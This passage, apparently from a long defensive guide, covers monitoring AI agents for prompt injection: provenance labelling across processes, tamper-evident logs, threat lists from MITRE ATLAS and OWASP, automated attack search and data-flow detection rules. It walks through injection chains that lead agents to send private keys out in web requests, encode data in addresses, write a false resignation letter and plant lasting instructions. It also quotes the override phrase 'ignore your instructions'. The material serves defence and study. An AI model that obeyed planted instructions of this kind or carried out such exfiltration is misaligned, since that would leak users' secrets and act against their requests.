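AgentSight loses this connection for two reasons. The scheduler doesn't descend from the agent, so the second eBPF program drops the scheduler's events. Even if AgentSight collected them, the gap of an hour is far longer than its half-second window. The script's name might still match something in the model's response, but matching text is weak evidence that two records refer to the same file.

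AgentLoupe attaches a label to the things that the agent touches:

1. When an eBPF program captures a new prompt, it assigns a number to that interaction and labels the part of the agent's program that sent it.
2. Any process that a labelled process starts inherits the label.
3. When a labelled process writes to a file, the software stores the label in a kernel table under that file's identity.
4. Any process that later opens or runs the file picks up the label, whoever started the process and however much time has passed. Labels also travel over network sockets, the endpoints through which processes exchange data.

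The script in the example therefore carries the label of the interaction that produced it. The scheduler's process picks up the label when it opens the script, and the outgoing connection inherits it. In a test of this attack, AgentLoupe traced the connection back to the original interaction. It also linked two sessions, one in which a malicious instruction was written into a file that coding agents read when they start work, and another in which an agent followed that instruction.

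If every process that opens a labelled file passes the label on, much of the machine may end up labelled, and the label no longer identifies anything. AgentLoupe limits this by starting a new number with each independent prompt and storing only a pointer to the earlier number. Bao and colleagues haven't measured how often labels spread wrongly or get lost, and their evidence consists of the two cases above. They also infer AgentSight's failure from its design and leave a side-by-side test on such attacks to future work.

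Both systems slowed agents by less than 8% on average. AgentLoupe added 4.5% to the time an agent took to study a code repository, 8.0% to writing code and 7.7% to compiling a program. AgentSight added 4.5%, 2.5% and 1.7% to the same tasks. The slowdown looks acceptable on servers where agents can create scheduled jobs or edit files that later sessions will read. Both systems were tested on Linux, but Uber's deployment covers MacBooks, so a company with a similar fleet couldn't simply install either one in place of ADR's sensor.

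### Links to the wrong process

A wrong link in the record can be worse than a missing one because it can implicate an agent or employee that had nothing to do with the attack. *ExecWeave* (Wong and Chen, 2026) presents a recorder designed to reduce this risk by keeping an agent's reports separate from activity observed at the operating-system level. The separation matters because, for example, a framework's record of a command doesn't prove that the command ran.

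To connect the two, ExecWeave takes a command from the agent's trace and looks for matching processes that started within the next three seconds. If exactly one process matches, it adds a link and marks it as inferred. If several match, it adds no link. Always picking the nearest match would produce a tidier graph, but some of the links would be false.

This caution fails when the recorder misses the real process. Suppose two agents run the same program at about the same time, and the recorder captures only the second run. That run is now the only match, so ExecWeave links it to the first agent's command. Wong and Chen deleted the real process from the data, left a similar one in place, and confirmed that the software could add the wrong link.

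A recorder that takes periodic snapshots, as ExecWeave's portable version does, often misses processes. For processes that lasted about 16 milliseconds, that version caught 18 of 30 when it checked every 20 milliseconds and none of 30 when it checked every half second. It also added between 62% and 409% to the running time of test jobs with many file operations and new processes. An attacker's command can easily finish within 16 milliseconds, so a recorder that the kernel notifies of each event is a better choice for a team that needs dependable links. AgentSight and AgentLoupe both work that way.

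Storing the type of evidence behind each link is useful with any recorder. ExecWeave grades its evidence from A, for a system call that a specific process made, down to D, for an inference. The grade measures how well the evidence supports the link, not how harmful the action was. In the sample trace, the line saying that process 8812 opened the key would get an A if the kernel reported it, while a guess that call 2 caused it would get a D.

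### Late, missing and altered records

The sample attack lasts 13 seconds from request to reply. With an hourly sensor, the trace arrives half an hour later on average, which is soon enough for an investigation but too late to stop the key from leaving. Li and colleagues found that credentials had often already left Uber by the time a detection surfaced. Uber then used hooks, points at which Cursor and Claude Code run a company's own script, to scan prompts for secrets and block them before they reach the agent. It still used the sensor for deeper investigations.

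Gaps in the record often come from trying to save money. Performance engineers commonly keep only a small sample of traces, which works because a slow service is slow for many requests, but an attack may occur in only one session. *Security Considerations for Multi-agent Systems* adds that the evidence can lie in the connection between several agents' traces. If three agents each independently keep a random 10% of their traces, an attack that leaves one trace with each agent will be fully recorded only 0.1% of the time. A better way to save money is to keep the tool names, arguments and hashes from every session, and to store bulky content elsewhere for a shorter time.

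Comparing logs from independent recorders can reveal some gaps. If the kernel records a connection from the agent's process but the framework trace has no matching call, either the trace is incomplete or something bypassed the framework, and both possibilities are worth investigating.

The agent may also be able to change the record. ADR's sensor reads files on the employee's laptop, and a coding agent that runs under the employee's account can usually write to the same folders. A planted instruction could cause the agent to delete the relevant entries before the sensor collects them, which might not happen for another hour. Kernel recorders are harder to tamper with because changing them normally requires administrator rights.

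A hash chain makes changes to a log detectable. Each entry includes a hash, or short fingerprint, of the entry before it. If someone edits entry 40, its hash no longer matches the one stored in entry 41. But an intruder who controls the whole log could recompute every later hash, so the team also has to keep a recent hash somewhere the intruder can't write. Wong and Chen acknowledge that ExecWeave's file of hashes has this weakness when it is stored in the same writable place as the evidence.

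Bindschaedler and colleagues regularly publish such a hash on a public blockchain, which costs $2.30 per 100,000 events. Their full system detected every edit, deletion and reordering in their tests, and added about 48 microseconds and 512 bytes per event. The blockchain is for disputes between organisations with no referee they both trust. Bindschaedler and colleagues say a hash chain is enough for a company's own investigations if the log goes to write-once storage.

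This protects only entries from before the intruder took over the machine. A compromised recorder can write false entries with valid hashes, and a hash chain can't reveal an event that never reached the log. Sending each entry to another machine immediately, rather than hourly, leaves less history exposed to tampering.

### Secrets in the logs

A complete trace of the ticket attack would contain the private key twice, in the result of the file read and in the outgoing request. Anyone who can search the logs could copy the key. Traces also contain source code, customer records and whatever employees type to their agents, so a central store of them would be a valuable target for attackers.

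OpenTelemetry leaves prompts and outputs out of traces by default, which protects privacy but removes the evidence they contain. For production systems that need the content, OpenTelemetry recommends storing it separately and putting only a reference in the trace. Engineers who monitor an agent's speed can then read the traces without access to the prompts.

Uber keeps the content of its traces but restricts its use. According to Li and colleagues, automated scanning removes secrets where possible, and only security staff have access, each with the minimum they need. Uber encrypts the data on its way to storage and deletes it after 13 months. Its legal, privacy and risk teams reviewed the system before deployment.

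There is a case for keeping employees' prompts for as long as thirteen months. The agency behind the Australian portal that Goli describes heard about its incident twelve weeks afterwards, and a false entry in an agent's memory can lie unused for longer than that. A company that deletes traces after 30 days would have no traces left to examine in either case. Removing secrets is the weaker part of Uber's approach. Scanners detect keys and tokens far better than confidential customer histories, so the access rules have to protect everything the scanners leave in.

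Staff can be given access to individual recorded events rather than to all or none of them. Bindschaedler and colleagues encrypt the content of each event with a separate key, so an auditor investigating three events out of a thousand can be given only those three keys. However, the keys for a batch of events all derive from one batch key, and anyone who obtains that key, for instance through a court order, can read the whole batch.

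## Predicting how attacks on an agent will look

Complete traces help a detector only if someone has identified which events in them would point to an attack. The planted text is hard to predict because an attacker can reword it, translate it or put it in another medium, such as an image. Yang and colleagues cite an experiment in which altered images and sounds steered a model to the attacker's chosen output 98% of the time. The agent's next actions are easier to predict because they have to go through tools the defender can list in advance.

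### Why actions are easier to predict than text

An agent can send mail or delete a file only through a tool call, which Yang and colleagues write as

Invoke(T, θ, C) → (o, Δ)

where a tool T runs with arguments θ in a context C, which includes the credentials it can use. It returns an output o and causes side effects Δ, such as a sent message. An attacker is after a particular Δ, and only some combinations of tool and arguments can produce it. A defender who knows the tools can write those combinations down without knowing anything about the planted text.

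For the theft of data, three events have to happen:

- Text from the attacker reaches the agent.
- The agent reads the secret or refers to it, for instance by attaching a file that it never opened.
- The agent makes a call whose effects the attacker can see.

The first two events can come in either order. In the ticket attack, the three events are reading the ticket, reading the key and making the web request.

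As with the key repair, a harmless session can contain the same kinds of events, so the team still needs to see the user's request to tell an attack from ordinary work.

The argument is weaker for an agent with a command line. The command line is a single tool, but its input can be any program, so nobody can list all the possible calls. The team then has to predict system events, such as opened files and outgoing connections. The argument also fails when the damage comes from the agent's reply. A hijacked agent can give an employee the wrong bank details for a supplier and leave the employee to make the payment, without any suspicious call in the trace.

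### Four steps, worked through for an office assistant

A team can turn this reasoning into a procedure:

1. List what the agent can reach, and the harm it could do there.
2. List what an outsider can write that the agent will read.
3. Trace the steps that lead from each outside text to each harm.
4. For each step, write down what it must leave in the trace, whatever the wording of the planted text.

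Suppose that a company's finance staff use an assistant with mail, files and web access. The first list might look like this:

| Tool | What the assistant can read | What it can change or send |
|---|---|---|
| Mail | The employee's whole mailbox | Messages to anyone, in the employee's name |
| Files | Contracts, payroll, suppliers' bank details | New, edited or deleted files, and links that let outsiders in |
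| Web | Any public page | The address it requests, which the site's owner can log |

The case in the bottom right cell is easy to overlook. A tool that only fetches pages can still send data out, because the web address it requests can contain data.

OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) is a starting point for the second list. It names emails and attachments, calendar invitations, shared documents, forums, social media posts and any web page as places where the company's browser agent may encounter hostile instructions. Some of these require more of the attacker than others. Anyone can email the finance assistant, but a web page matters only if the assistant visits it. Teams also tend to forget outside text that has been copied into internal systems. If an employee saves a supplier's attachment to the company drive, the drive will probably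 record the employee as its owner.

An assistant could read three kinds of outside text (emails, web pages and shared documents) and cause four kinds of harm: leaking a confidential file, sending a false message, changing a supplier's bank details or deleting files. Pairing each kind of text with each kind of harm gives 12 pairs to trace. The path from an email to a stolen payroll file is short. The assistant reads the email, retrieves the file and sends it out in one of three ways: by email, through a sharing link or in a web address.

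The fourth step is the hardest, because many signs that look reliable are ones the attacker can remove. A useful test is to ask whether the attack would still work without them:

| Possible sign | Could the attacker avoid it and still get the payroll file? |
|---|---|
| The email contains a phrase like "ignore your instructions" | Yes, by rewording it |
| The assistant's stated reasoning mentions the email | Yes, since stated reasons can be incomplete |
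| The outgoing text matches the file | Yes, if the assistant summarises the file first |
| The assistant contacts a new address | Yes, through a service that the company already uses |
| The assistant reads text from outside | Only if the text arrived earlier, or carries an internal label |
| The assistant opens, attaches or shares the payroll file | Only if a copy exists elsewhere, such as in an old email |
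| A mail, sharing or web call delivers something to a place outsiders can read | No |

The prediction from the last three rows is that, after reading text from outside, the assistant will open, attach or share a payroll file that the request didn't call for, and then make a call that delivers something to a place outsiders can read. The two exceptions go back into the lists, so the team should also look for old copies of the payroll file and for outside documents with internal labels.

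A list of harms can easily be too short, as OpenAI's demonstration shows. An attacker puts a malicious email in a user's inbox, and the user later asks the browser agent to write an out-of-office reply. The agent reads the email during this task and sends the user's chief executive a resignation letter instead. The payroll prediction would miss this attack because the agent opens no confidential file and the message need not leave the company. The predicted path from an email to a false message would cover it, as long as the team had written "sends a message that the request did not call for" and hadn't limited the prediction to outside recipients.

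### Published lists of attacks

The procedure depends on what the team can think of, so it helps to compare the results with attacks that others have recorded. MITRE, a US non-profit research organisation, maintains a public knowledge base of attacks on AI systems called ATLAS (unrelated to OpenAI's browser). ATLAS groups techniques, which are methods of attack, under tactics, which are the attacker's aims at each stage. MITRE's *Updates* (2025) lists several new techniques specific to agents, including taking credentials from an agent's configuration and sending data out through its tools. Zenity, a security company that worked on these entries with MITRE, explains that an attacker can have sensitive data encoded in the arguments of a call that looks legitimate, such as one that sends an email, edits a document or updates a customer record. This suggests an ending the team may have missed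 for the finance assistant, which could write the payroll data into a document that outsiders can already open.

Cunningham and Dotter (2026), in *MITRE ATLAS Grows through Collaboration with CTID and Industry*, count more than 45 techniques and sub-techniques and more than 20 case studies added to ATLAS during one phase of work with industry, which ended with the April 2026 updates. MITRE now publishes a new version of ATLAS every month, and users can filter techniques by maturity.

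MITRE (2026) also investigated OpenClaw, an open-source agent that acts across its user's applications. It examined four cases dated within ten days of each other:

- A researcher found hundreds of control panels open to the internet, with stored credentials in reach.
- Researchers published an add-on with a malicious prompt hidden inside, and it passed 4,000 downloads within an hour.
- A researcher showed that a single click on a crafted link could lead to control of the whole computer.
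- The security company HiddenLayer used a web page to make the agent run commands and plant lasting instructions in its own future prompts.

The techniques that recurred were prompt injection, tool invocation and changes to the agent's configuration. Sundar (2026), in *MITRE ATLAS OpenClaw Investigation Discovers New and Likeliest Techniques*, calls the ones that attackers rely on "chokepoint techniques". They are good places to concentrate monitoring because one detector can cover several attack paths. For example, HiddenLayer's attack must write to the agent's standing instructions to persist, and few ordinary tasks do that.

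All four cases came from researchers, so they are better evidence of what is possible than of what criminals do. MITRE labels most of the techniques involved "Demonstrated", but it labels supply-chain compromise and exfiltration through an agent's tools "Realized", meaning they have been used in real incidents. Incident reports in general cover only attacks that somebody noticed and chose to publish, but they give an attack's steps in order, which ATLAS's individual entries don't.

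Another weakness of ATLAS is that a single entry can cover many different attacks. A team with a rule for outgoing mail might mark "exfiltration via AI agent tool invocation" as covered and still miss data sent out through sharing links or web addresses. The MITRE centre where Sundar directs research found the same problem in ordinary intrusions. Its case study of the hacking group Volt Typhoon showed that defenders can cover most techniques and still miss some of the ways to carry them out.

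OWASP, an open community for software security, publishes a shorter list. In *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications*, Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario (2025) list ten risks: goal hijacking, tool misuse, abuse of identity and privilege, supply-chain weaknesses, unexpected code execution, poisoned memory or context, insecure communication between agents, cascading failures, exploitation of people's trust in agents, and rogue agents. They state that "these are not theoretical risks" and name an incident for six of them, but not for identity abuse, insecure communication between agents, cascading failures or exploited trust.

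The categories are too broad to search for in a trace, since "tool misuse" doesn't specify a tool or a call. They are more useful for checking a finished set of paths for gaps. For instance, none of the finance assistant's 12 pairs involves exploited trust, and a team that asks why will quickly think of the false bank details in a reply. The list also includes agents that go wrong without an attacker, which a team will overlook if it starts from outside text.

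Li and colleagues drew up their own list for Uber, with 17 techniques under five tactics. The table also gives the number of test attacks of each kind that Uber's detector caught:

| Tactic | Techniques | Example | Attacks caught |
|---|---|---|---|
| Initial access and execution | 6 | A tool changes its behaviour after approval | 13 of 19 |
| Permission abuse | 2 | One agent poses as another | 1 of 5 |
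| Security control bypass | 3 | A malicious tool interferes with a trusted one | 5 of 5 |
| Reasoning and data manipulation | 4 | An attacker plants false data | 5 of 9 |
| Operational impact | 2 | An agent uses up computing resources | 4 of 4 |

The numbers are small, but the result for permission abuse shows that putting a technique on a list doesn't make it detectable.

Li and colleagues find that eight earlier sets of test attacks each cover between three and six of the 17 techniques on their list, while their own set covers all 17. They built their set from the list, so full coverage was certain. The list draws on ATLAS, OWASP, published incidents, Uber's telemetry and conversations with staff who stage mock attacks. A technique that appears in this list, ATLAS and OWASP may therefore have only one original source. The telemetry showed that leaks of credentials and other data were fairly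 common at Uber, which the company couldn't have learned from ATLAS or OWASP.

### Attackers with better tools

Records of past attacks are a weak guide to what attackers will be able to do next year. In April 2026, the UK's AI Security Institute reported that Claude Mythos Preview had completed a 32-step simulated attack on a small company network in 3 of 10 attempts. The institute estimated that the attack would take a person 20 hours. By December, the institute's *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026) reported that both models had broken into a much better protected network in every completed run. *GPT-6.2 Astra ‘blew through’ the UK’s hardest cyber test in five hours* (Constantin, 2026) gives GPT-6.2 Astra's count as 12 out of 12. The institute had turned the models' safeguards off, nobody was defending the network, and a setup error gave the models extra access at the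 start.

These tests involved break-ins to networks rather than hijacked agents, so they don't show what an attack on a mail assistant would leave in its trace. But given their results, the need for days of skilled work is no longer a good reason for a team to cross out a possible attack path. Constantin reports that Britain's National Cyber Security Centre has told organisations to reassess their resilience now.

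The December result also suggests that a company listing the paths into its finance assistant by hand will miss some. The institute hadn't planted any route into the network, and the models found their own.

### Automated search for attacks

Software can search for missing paths, usually in a loop that generates many variants of an attack, runs each against a copy of the agent in a closed test environment, scores the results, and makes new variants from the best ones. The Explorer, the offline part of Uber's system, divides this work among three language-model agents. The first proposes variants by combining known attacks and changing their details. The second runs each variant in isolation and records whether it worked and whether the detector caught it. The third turns the most valuable finds into guidance for the detector, such as a note to watch a particular kind of tool for access to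 secrets.

Li and colleagues score each variant with the formula

F = ε · σ · τ^α

Here ε is how far the attack got, σ is how natural it looked, τ is how much damage it could do, and α = 1.2 sets the weight of the damage.

Here are two invented variants of an attack on the finance assistant, with each quantity on a scale from 0 to 1. Variant A gets the assistant to send out a list of the company's suppliers. It nearly always works and looks like routine mail, but the list isn't very sensitive. Variant B targets the payroll file and usually stops halfway.

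| | ε | σ | τ | F if α = 1 | F if α = 1.2 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A: supplier list | 0.9 | 0.8 | 0.4 | 0.288 | 0.240 |
| B: payroll file | 0.5 | 0.6 | 0.9 | 0.270 | 0.264 |

For variant A, 0.4^1.2 is 0.333, so F = 0.9 × 0.8 × 0.333 = 0.240. With α = 1, A would have the higher score. Raising α to 1.2 reverses the order, because on this scale it lowers the score of a low-damage attack much more than that of a high-damage one. If the search keeps only one variant, it will continue developing the payroll attack and drop the one that already works.

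That is a sensible priority for a company that cares most about large losses, but quiet attacks with small effects will tend to drop out of the results. Because the formula multiplies its terms, a variant that fails at the first step scores close to zero, even if one small change would have made it work.

The search also has to stop. In each round, a share ρ of the variants survives, and each survivor produces μ mutations. If each round tests only the new mutations, N variants in one round lead to ρμN in the next. Li and colleagues require ρμ to be below 1, so that this number shrinks. With ρ = 0.2 and μ = 4, ρμ is 0.8, so a search that starts with 100 variants tests 80, 64 and 51 in the next three rounds, and the number falls below one after 21 rounds. In total, the search tests about 100 / (1 − 0.8) = 500 variants.

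This calculation doesn't depend on how many attacks would work, so the search ends after about 500 variants whether the assistant has ten weaknesses or ten thousand. Li and colleagues describe the end as convergence, but their condition guarantees only that the search runs out of variants, not that it has found everything worth finding. Since each variant is a changed or combined version of a known attack, the search is also likely to miss methods unlike any of the known ones.

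Some evidence suggests that written guidance of this kind helps. When Li and colleagues cut off the detector from its store of known attack methods, recall on their test fell from 67% to 59%. But that store holds analysts' notes as well as the Explorer's finds, so the drop doesn't show how much the Explorer contributed. The test attacks also came from the same 17 techniques as the store, so the test measures only how much the store helps with expected attacks.

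### An attacker trained against a browser agent

OpenAI went further and trained a language model to be the attacker. It used reinforcement learning, in which a model tries something, receives a reward if it succeeds, and becomes more likely to repeat what worked. The target was the browser agent in ChatGPT Atlas. Before the attacker commits to an injection, it can try out drafts:

1. The attacker writes a candidate injection and sends it to a simulator.
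2. The simulator works out how the browser agent would behave if it came across that text.
3. The attacker gets back the agent's full reasoning and actions, which give it much more to work with than a simple pass or fail.
4. It revises the injection and repeats the process several times before choosing a final version.

According to OpenAI, most earlier automated attacks produced simple failures, such as a particular phrase in the output or one unintended tool call. The trained attacker could lead the agent through harmful tasks of tens or hundreds of steps. It also used strategies that had not appeared in OpenAI's human testing or in outside reports. The resignation letter was one of the attacks it found. OpenAI then trained a new version of the browser agent to resist these attacks, and used the records of successful attacks to look for ways to improve monitoring.

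This is better evidence than the Explorer that a search can find attacks people haven't listed. But it is a company's account of its own product, and it gives no success rates or number of attacks found. The method is also hard for a customer to copy, because OpenAI's attacker uses a great deal of computing power and learns from the browser agent's private reasoning, which the company doesn't disclose to outsiders. Most companies will have to use simpler searches and the results that larger companies publish.

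When a search finds an attack, a monitoring team should record the sequence of actions and pay less attention to the exact wording. The wording of the resignation email will probably never recur, but any attack with the same aim has to make the agent send a message that the user didn't ask for. Searches aimed at a particular detector raise separate problems, which are part of testing detectors. OpenAI expects attackers to keep adapting, and considers prompt injection "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'".

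### Attacks that the procedure misses

The four steps will miss an attack unless an outsider plants text and the agent then causes harm through calls in its trace. The agents in the Hugging Face intrusion were trying to solve a test, according to OpenAI's technical report, so there was no attacker's text to list in the second step.

Malicious tools break the other assumption. Yang and colleagues describe tools that do their advertised job but contain hidden code that runs only under certain conditions. The agent picks the right tool, passes sensible arguments and gives a coherent explanation, while the hidden code does something else. They add that installing a tool often installs other packages, which can run their own code before the agent calls the tool. The agent's trace may not record either kind of code running. To detect it, the team needs system events from the machine where the tool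 runs, which it may not have if the tool is remote.

The lists also go out of date. If someone connects the finance assistant to a calendar in March, outsiders can then reach it through invitations, which a list from January won't include. The team should therefore repeat the procedure whenever an agent gets a new tool.

### Scoring the predictions

Almost any attack looks predictable after the incident, so a team that wants to measure how good its predictions are has to write them down beforehand, with a date, and later count how many incidents they covered. OpenClaw's published *Threat model (MITRE ATLAS)* could serve as such a record. It applies ATLAS and data-flow diagrams to the agent, its messaging channels and its add-on marketplace. Contributors can report new threats and the document can be revised, so anyone who wants to score it needs a copy from before the incident.

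The result depends heavily on what counts as covered. For example, by October 2025 MITRE's ATLAS already included prompt injection, tool invocation and the theft of credentials from an agent's configuration. At least one of these played a part in three of the four OpenClaw cases a few months later (the open control panels, the poisoned add-on and HiddenLayer's web page), so ATLAS did well if one listed technique is enough for a case to count as covered. But MITRE needed seven new techniques to describe the four cases, so ATLAS would do much worse if techniques were counted instead of cases.

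For monitoring, it makes sense to use a stricter rule and count an incident as covered only if a prediction specified an event that appeared in the trace before the harm was done. A prediction that "the agent will misuse a tool" wouldn't count, because it doesn't specify an event. The team should also count how many harmless sessions match each prediction. A prediction that matches 40 harmless sessions out of 10,000 can lead to a usable alert, but 6,000 matches would mean too many false alarms, however many attacks the prediction covers.

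Suppose the finance team writes 12 predictions in January and by July learns of eight incidents involving similar assistants. If the predictions covered five of the eight, the score is 63%. With so few incidents, the 95% confidence interval runs from about 31% to 86%, which is far too wide for comparing one year's score with the next.

The three misses are more useful than the percentage because each can be traced to a step of the procedure. One attack may have come through a calendar invitation, which the team left off its list of outside text. Another may have used a sharing permission that the team left off its list of what the assistant could reach. For the third, the team may have predicted the right event but found that the trace didn't record it.

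The score will usually overstate how accurate the predictions are, because an attack that nobody predicted is also less likely to be noticed, and unnoticed attacks aren't counted. Mock attacks by people who haven't read the predictions can correct for some of this. The team should score mock attacks separately from real incidents, because the testers choose which attacks to try.

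## Writing rules and setting tripwires for expected attacks

A prediction that specifies events in the trace is already most of a detection rule. For the ticket attack, the prediction is that the agent will read text from outside, read something private, and then send something to a destination that is new to the company. In pseudocode:

```
at the start of a session:
    outside_text = no
    private_data = no

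for each tool call, in order:
    if the call sends something
       and the destination is new to the company
       and outside_text = yes
       and private_data = yes:
           raise an alert
    if the result came from outside:   outside_text = yes
    if the result is private:          private_data = yes
```

The trace shows where each result came from and where each call goes, but the team has to list which files and databases count as private and work out what each tool can do. *Parasites in the Toolchain* (2025), a study of public MCP servers, sorts tools by whether they can bring in outside content, read private data, or send data out.

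Here is the rule on four invented sessions:

| Session | Outside text | Private data | New destination | Alert? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Summary of an ordinary ticket | Yes | No | No | No |
| Reply to a known customer about an order | Yes | Yes | No | No |
| Key repair, on a ticket with a comment from the hosting company | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes (false alarm) |
| Ticket attack | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |

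The login test in the key repair has no field in which the agent could put the contents of a file, whereas the attack uses a web call with a body. One more condition removes the false alarm:

```
       and the call has room for the data
           (a body, an attachment or a long web address)
```

The team could instead require the key's fingerprint to appear in the outgoing call. This would also avoid an alert on the key repair, but an attacker could evade the rule by having the agent encode the key first. A matching fingerprint is more useful for moving an alert to the top of the queue. Exempting every address that the ticket mentions would be a mistake because the attacker wrote part of the ticket. Exempting addresses in the employee's own request is much safer.

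The refined rule still has flaws. It raises a false alarm if an employee asks the agent to send a private error log to a supplier's new support site. It misses an attacker who collects the key through a file-sharing service that the company already uses, unless the team defines a destination as a particular account or folder on that service. It also resets at the start of each session, so it misses instructions that entered the agent's memory in an earlier session. The team could fix this by storing the origin of each memory entry and setting `outside_text` when the agent loads an entry that came from outside.

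### Why rules about wording fail sooner

A rule that searches tickets for phrases like "ignore your instructions" is easier to write than the data-flow rule, but the attacker controls the phrasing. *AgentShield* (Rassul and Rashid, 2026) tested two classifiers trained to recognise injected text. Meta's Prompt Guard 2 caught about 1% of attacks in each of English, Kurdish and Arabic. ProtectAI's classifier caught 44.6% of attacks in English and flagged 2.1% of harmless English text. In Kurdish it caught 97.6% of attacks but also flagged 97.5% of harmless text, so it was mostly reacting to the language. Translating the ticket would not affect the data-flow rule, which never examines the wording.

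In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) compare prompt injection with SQL injection, an older attack in which a website's visitor types database commands into a form. Developers solved that problem by setting the structure of each query before adding the visitor's text, rather than by getting better at recognising malicious input. The database could then no longer run the text as a command. Ordinary language has no grammar that separates instructions from data, so the defences that Narisetty and colleagues favour check the agent's actions instead.

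Those defences depend heavily on correct labels. If an employee pastes a supplier's email into a request, the trace will record the text as the employee's own. Narisetty and colleagues also note that FIDES, a system for tracking data in agents, treats unlabelled text as trusted. Treating it as coming from outside is safer for monitoring, though it will produce some extra alerts.

### Limits on tools and arguments

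The data-flow rule raises no alert until the agent sends something. A permission rule can stop the ticket attack earlier, when the agent tries to open the key, because summarising a ticket requires only the ticket tool. Writing such rules by hand for every request would be impractical. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses a language model to draft the rules from the user's request. Ordinary software checks each call and blocks anything that no rule allows.

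In their main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice:

1. The first policy allows a single call, a search for Alice's email by sender and subject.
2. The email asks for a summary of recent mail, posted to the user's account on Slack, a messaging service. The model proposes allowing the tools for this. Because the new policy allows more than the old one, it needs approval.
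3. The agent looks up the user's Slack name. The model proposes allowing messages to that name only, and this takes effect automatically.
4. One of the recent emails contains a planted instruction to forward the inbox to an outsider. No rule allows the agent to send mail, so the software blocks the call and returns an error. The agent then posts the summary as intended.

A new policy takes effect without approval only if the current policy already allows every call that the new one allows. A solver, a program that checks logical formulas, compares the two. A planted instruction may cause the model to propose a wider policy, but that policy can't take effect without approval.

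With GPT-4o as the agent, Progent cut the success rate of attacks from 39.9% to 1.0% on AgentDojo, a public set of agent tasks with planted instructions, and from 70.3% to 3.9% on a second test set. In these tests, Shi and colleagues automatically approved every wider policy to imitate a careless user. Only 6% of updates on AgentDojo needed approval. A simpler defence that allowed or removed whole tools did worse, because it either removed a tool the task needed or allowed it with any arguments. In a small test by Narisetty and colleagues, an attack written with knowledge of Progent did no better than the standard ones.

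Many of the remaining failures involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools. Progent also can't stop an attack that needs only permitted calls, or one that puts false information in the agent's reply. If the employee had written "resolve this ticket" instead of "summarise" it, the agent would need permissions based on the ticket's own text, and security would depend on whoever approves them.

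A monitoring team could treat each blocked call as an alert, but an agent may also try a forbidden tool by mistake. Shi and colleagues measured completed tasks and successful attacks, so their results don't give a false-positive rate for these alerts.

### Uber's filter for secrets

Some secrets are recognisable wherever they appear. Uber's filter first looks for text in the format of a known kind of credential, then checks whether the text is random enough to be a real one. The usual measure of randomness is entropy:

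H = −Σ p(c) log₂ p(c)

where p(c) is the share of the string that consists of character c. Suppose a pattern matches `api_key=` followed by 16 characters. The placeholder "changemechangeme" has an entropy of 2.75 bits per character, while 16 different characters give 4 bits. With a threshold of 3.5 (an invented figure), the filter would ignore the placeholder and block the other string. It would also ignore a careless employee's real password if that password were "changemechangeme".

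Li and colleagues report that the filter, which can block a prompt before it reaches the coding agent, made 206 correct detections and 6 false ones across hundreds of thousands of sessions, a precision of 97.2%. They don't report how many secrets got through, so the filter's recall is unknown.

Uber moved from alerts to blocking partly because of the delay already described, and partly because there were soon too many credential alerts for analysts to review by hand. After a leak, the staff responsible had to replace the credential. Blocking the prompt avoids that work and usually doesn't require an analyst. Blocking is reasonable here because mistakes are rare and easy to fix. An employee whose prompt is wrongly blocked can remove the string and try again. A data-flow rule with more false alarms would interrupt legitimate work much more often, so it is better suited to alerts, at least at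 first.

The filter as described wouldn't stop the ticket attack, because the key enters through a file tool and never appears in the employee's prompt. A team could run the same patterns on the arguments of outgoing calls. Li and colleagues add that simple checks like this one miss attacks that can't be recognized without knowing what a tool does or what company policy allows.

### Alerts when a tool changes

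All of these rules depend on a tool still doing what it did when the company approved it. *ETDI* (2025), a proposal for signed tool definitions, gives the example of a wallpaper tool that keeps its name and version number but starts uploading financial documents. Programs that connect to MCP servers typically check a tool's definition when the user approves it and don't check again. According to *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, these programs also don't alert users when a definition changes.

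When the company approves a tool, the team stores a hash of its description, arguments and, where available, code, along with the address of its server. As a basic check, software compares the current values with the stored ones before each session.

Harmless tools change so often that an alert about a changed description will nearly always concern an ordinary update. Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, collected all 21,643 servers in the public MCP registry. Of the 8,900 with more than one version, 51.1% had changed what they advertised, and 40.6% had done so while their identifiers stayed the same. The median server that changed did so on the day it was first published. A scan of the code of 14,353 servers found no openly malicious instructions in tool descriptions, though it would have missed disguised ones.

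A team can block a server's move to a different host until somebody approves it, because such moves are rare. Only 4.2% of the servers with several versions changed hosts, and Kraishan thinks most of these moves were routine. When a tool's description changes, the software can show a reviewer the old and new text side by side. It should do this for every tool, because *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly* (2026), which followed a registry for 89 days, found that rechecking mainly the servers with a history of changes misses too much.

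Checking tool descriptions alone isn't enough, because the same call can have different effects in two versions of a tool. *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning* (2026) found that when an agent doesn't specify whether a new code repository should be public or private, version 1.3 of GitHub's MCP server makes it public and version 1.4 makes it private. A company that went back to version 1.3 could therefore publish its code through a call that had been safe in version 1.4. The descriptions of those two versions differed, but the study found other releases that had identical descriptions and different effects. Comparing code would reveal such a change, but the operator of a remote server can change its code without the company seeing it.

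### What a tool claims and what it does

A tool can also be misleading from the start, so checking for later changes won't catch it. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, built a checker that compares a tool's description with its code. It prompts a language model once to judge whether the two are consistent and again to judge whether they are inconsistent, then uses a third prompt to settle any disagreement. It flagged 9.93% of 19,200 tools. Most often, descriptions claimed features that the code lacked, which is a nuisance but seldom an attack. About a quarter of the mismatches were undeclared side effects, such as changing a file or uploading a query, which matter more to a security team.

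The checker had 96% precision and 97% recall on 400 tools that people labelled by hand. However, the checker had flagged half of these tools, a far higher share than in the full set. People found 5 real mismatches among the 200 unflagged tools in the sample. If that rate holds for the roughly 15,100 unflagged tools with descriptions, the checker missed about 380 mismatches and found about 1,830, a recall of about 83%.

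More general scanners do worse. Hu, Jia and colleagues (2026), in *MalTool*, used language models to write malicious code with 13 kinds of behaviour, such as stealing files, deleting data and slowing the computer. They inserted the code into 5,727 real tools, which kept working as advertised, and tested six scanners on the results. The table gives the share of attacks missed for two of the behaviours, and the share of 1,147 harmless code repositories that each scanner flagged:

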